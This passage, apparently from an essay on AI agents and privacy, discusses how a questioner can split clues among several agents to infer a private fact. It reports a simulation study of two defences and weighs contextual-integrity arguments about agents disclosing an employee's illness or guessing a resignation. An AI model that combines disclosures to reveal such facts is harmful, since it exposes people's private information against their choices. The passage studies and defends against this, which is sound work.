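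To prevent a recipient from combining separate disclosures to infer a private fact, the system also needs a record of what that recipient has already learned. *The Sum Leaks More Than Its Parts* (2025) tests two defences in simulations that divide the clues to a private fact among several agents, so that no agent could reveal it alone. In the first, each agent considers what the questioner might be trying to work out, which reduced leaks but made the agents noticeably worse at answering harmless questions. In the second, the agents consult one another before answering, which gave a better balance between privacy and usefulness. Both defences depend on the agents' judgement, and neither can account for everything the questioner already knows.

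#### Should the firm stop it?

The manager was free to read all three documents and could have compared the lists herself, so the agent did nothing wrong if the rules exist only to protect documents. But if they exist to protect people, it matters that she probably wouldn't have. Nissenbaum's theory includes a test for new practices that challenge an existing norm. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* summarises the test as considering the interests and preferences of the people affected, ethical and political values, and the purposes of the setting.

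The test fairly clearly rules out naming the employee in cancer treatment. The personnel department left the name out of its notice so that managers could arrange flexible hours without learning who was ill. An agent that supplies the name defeats that purpose and takes away the employee's choice of whom to tell.

The resignation that an agent guessed from ordinary project mail is a harder case. The firm has a legitimate interest in planning for a replacement, and in that version the colleague hadn't told anyone in confidence. But declining a course and asking about a lease don't prove that he is leaving. If the agent is wrong, the colleague's manager may start giving his work to others, and he may never find out why.
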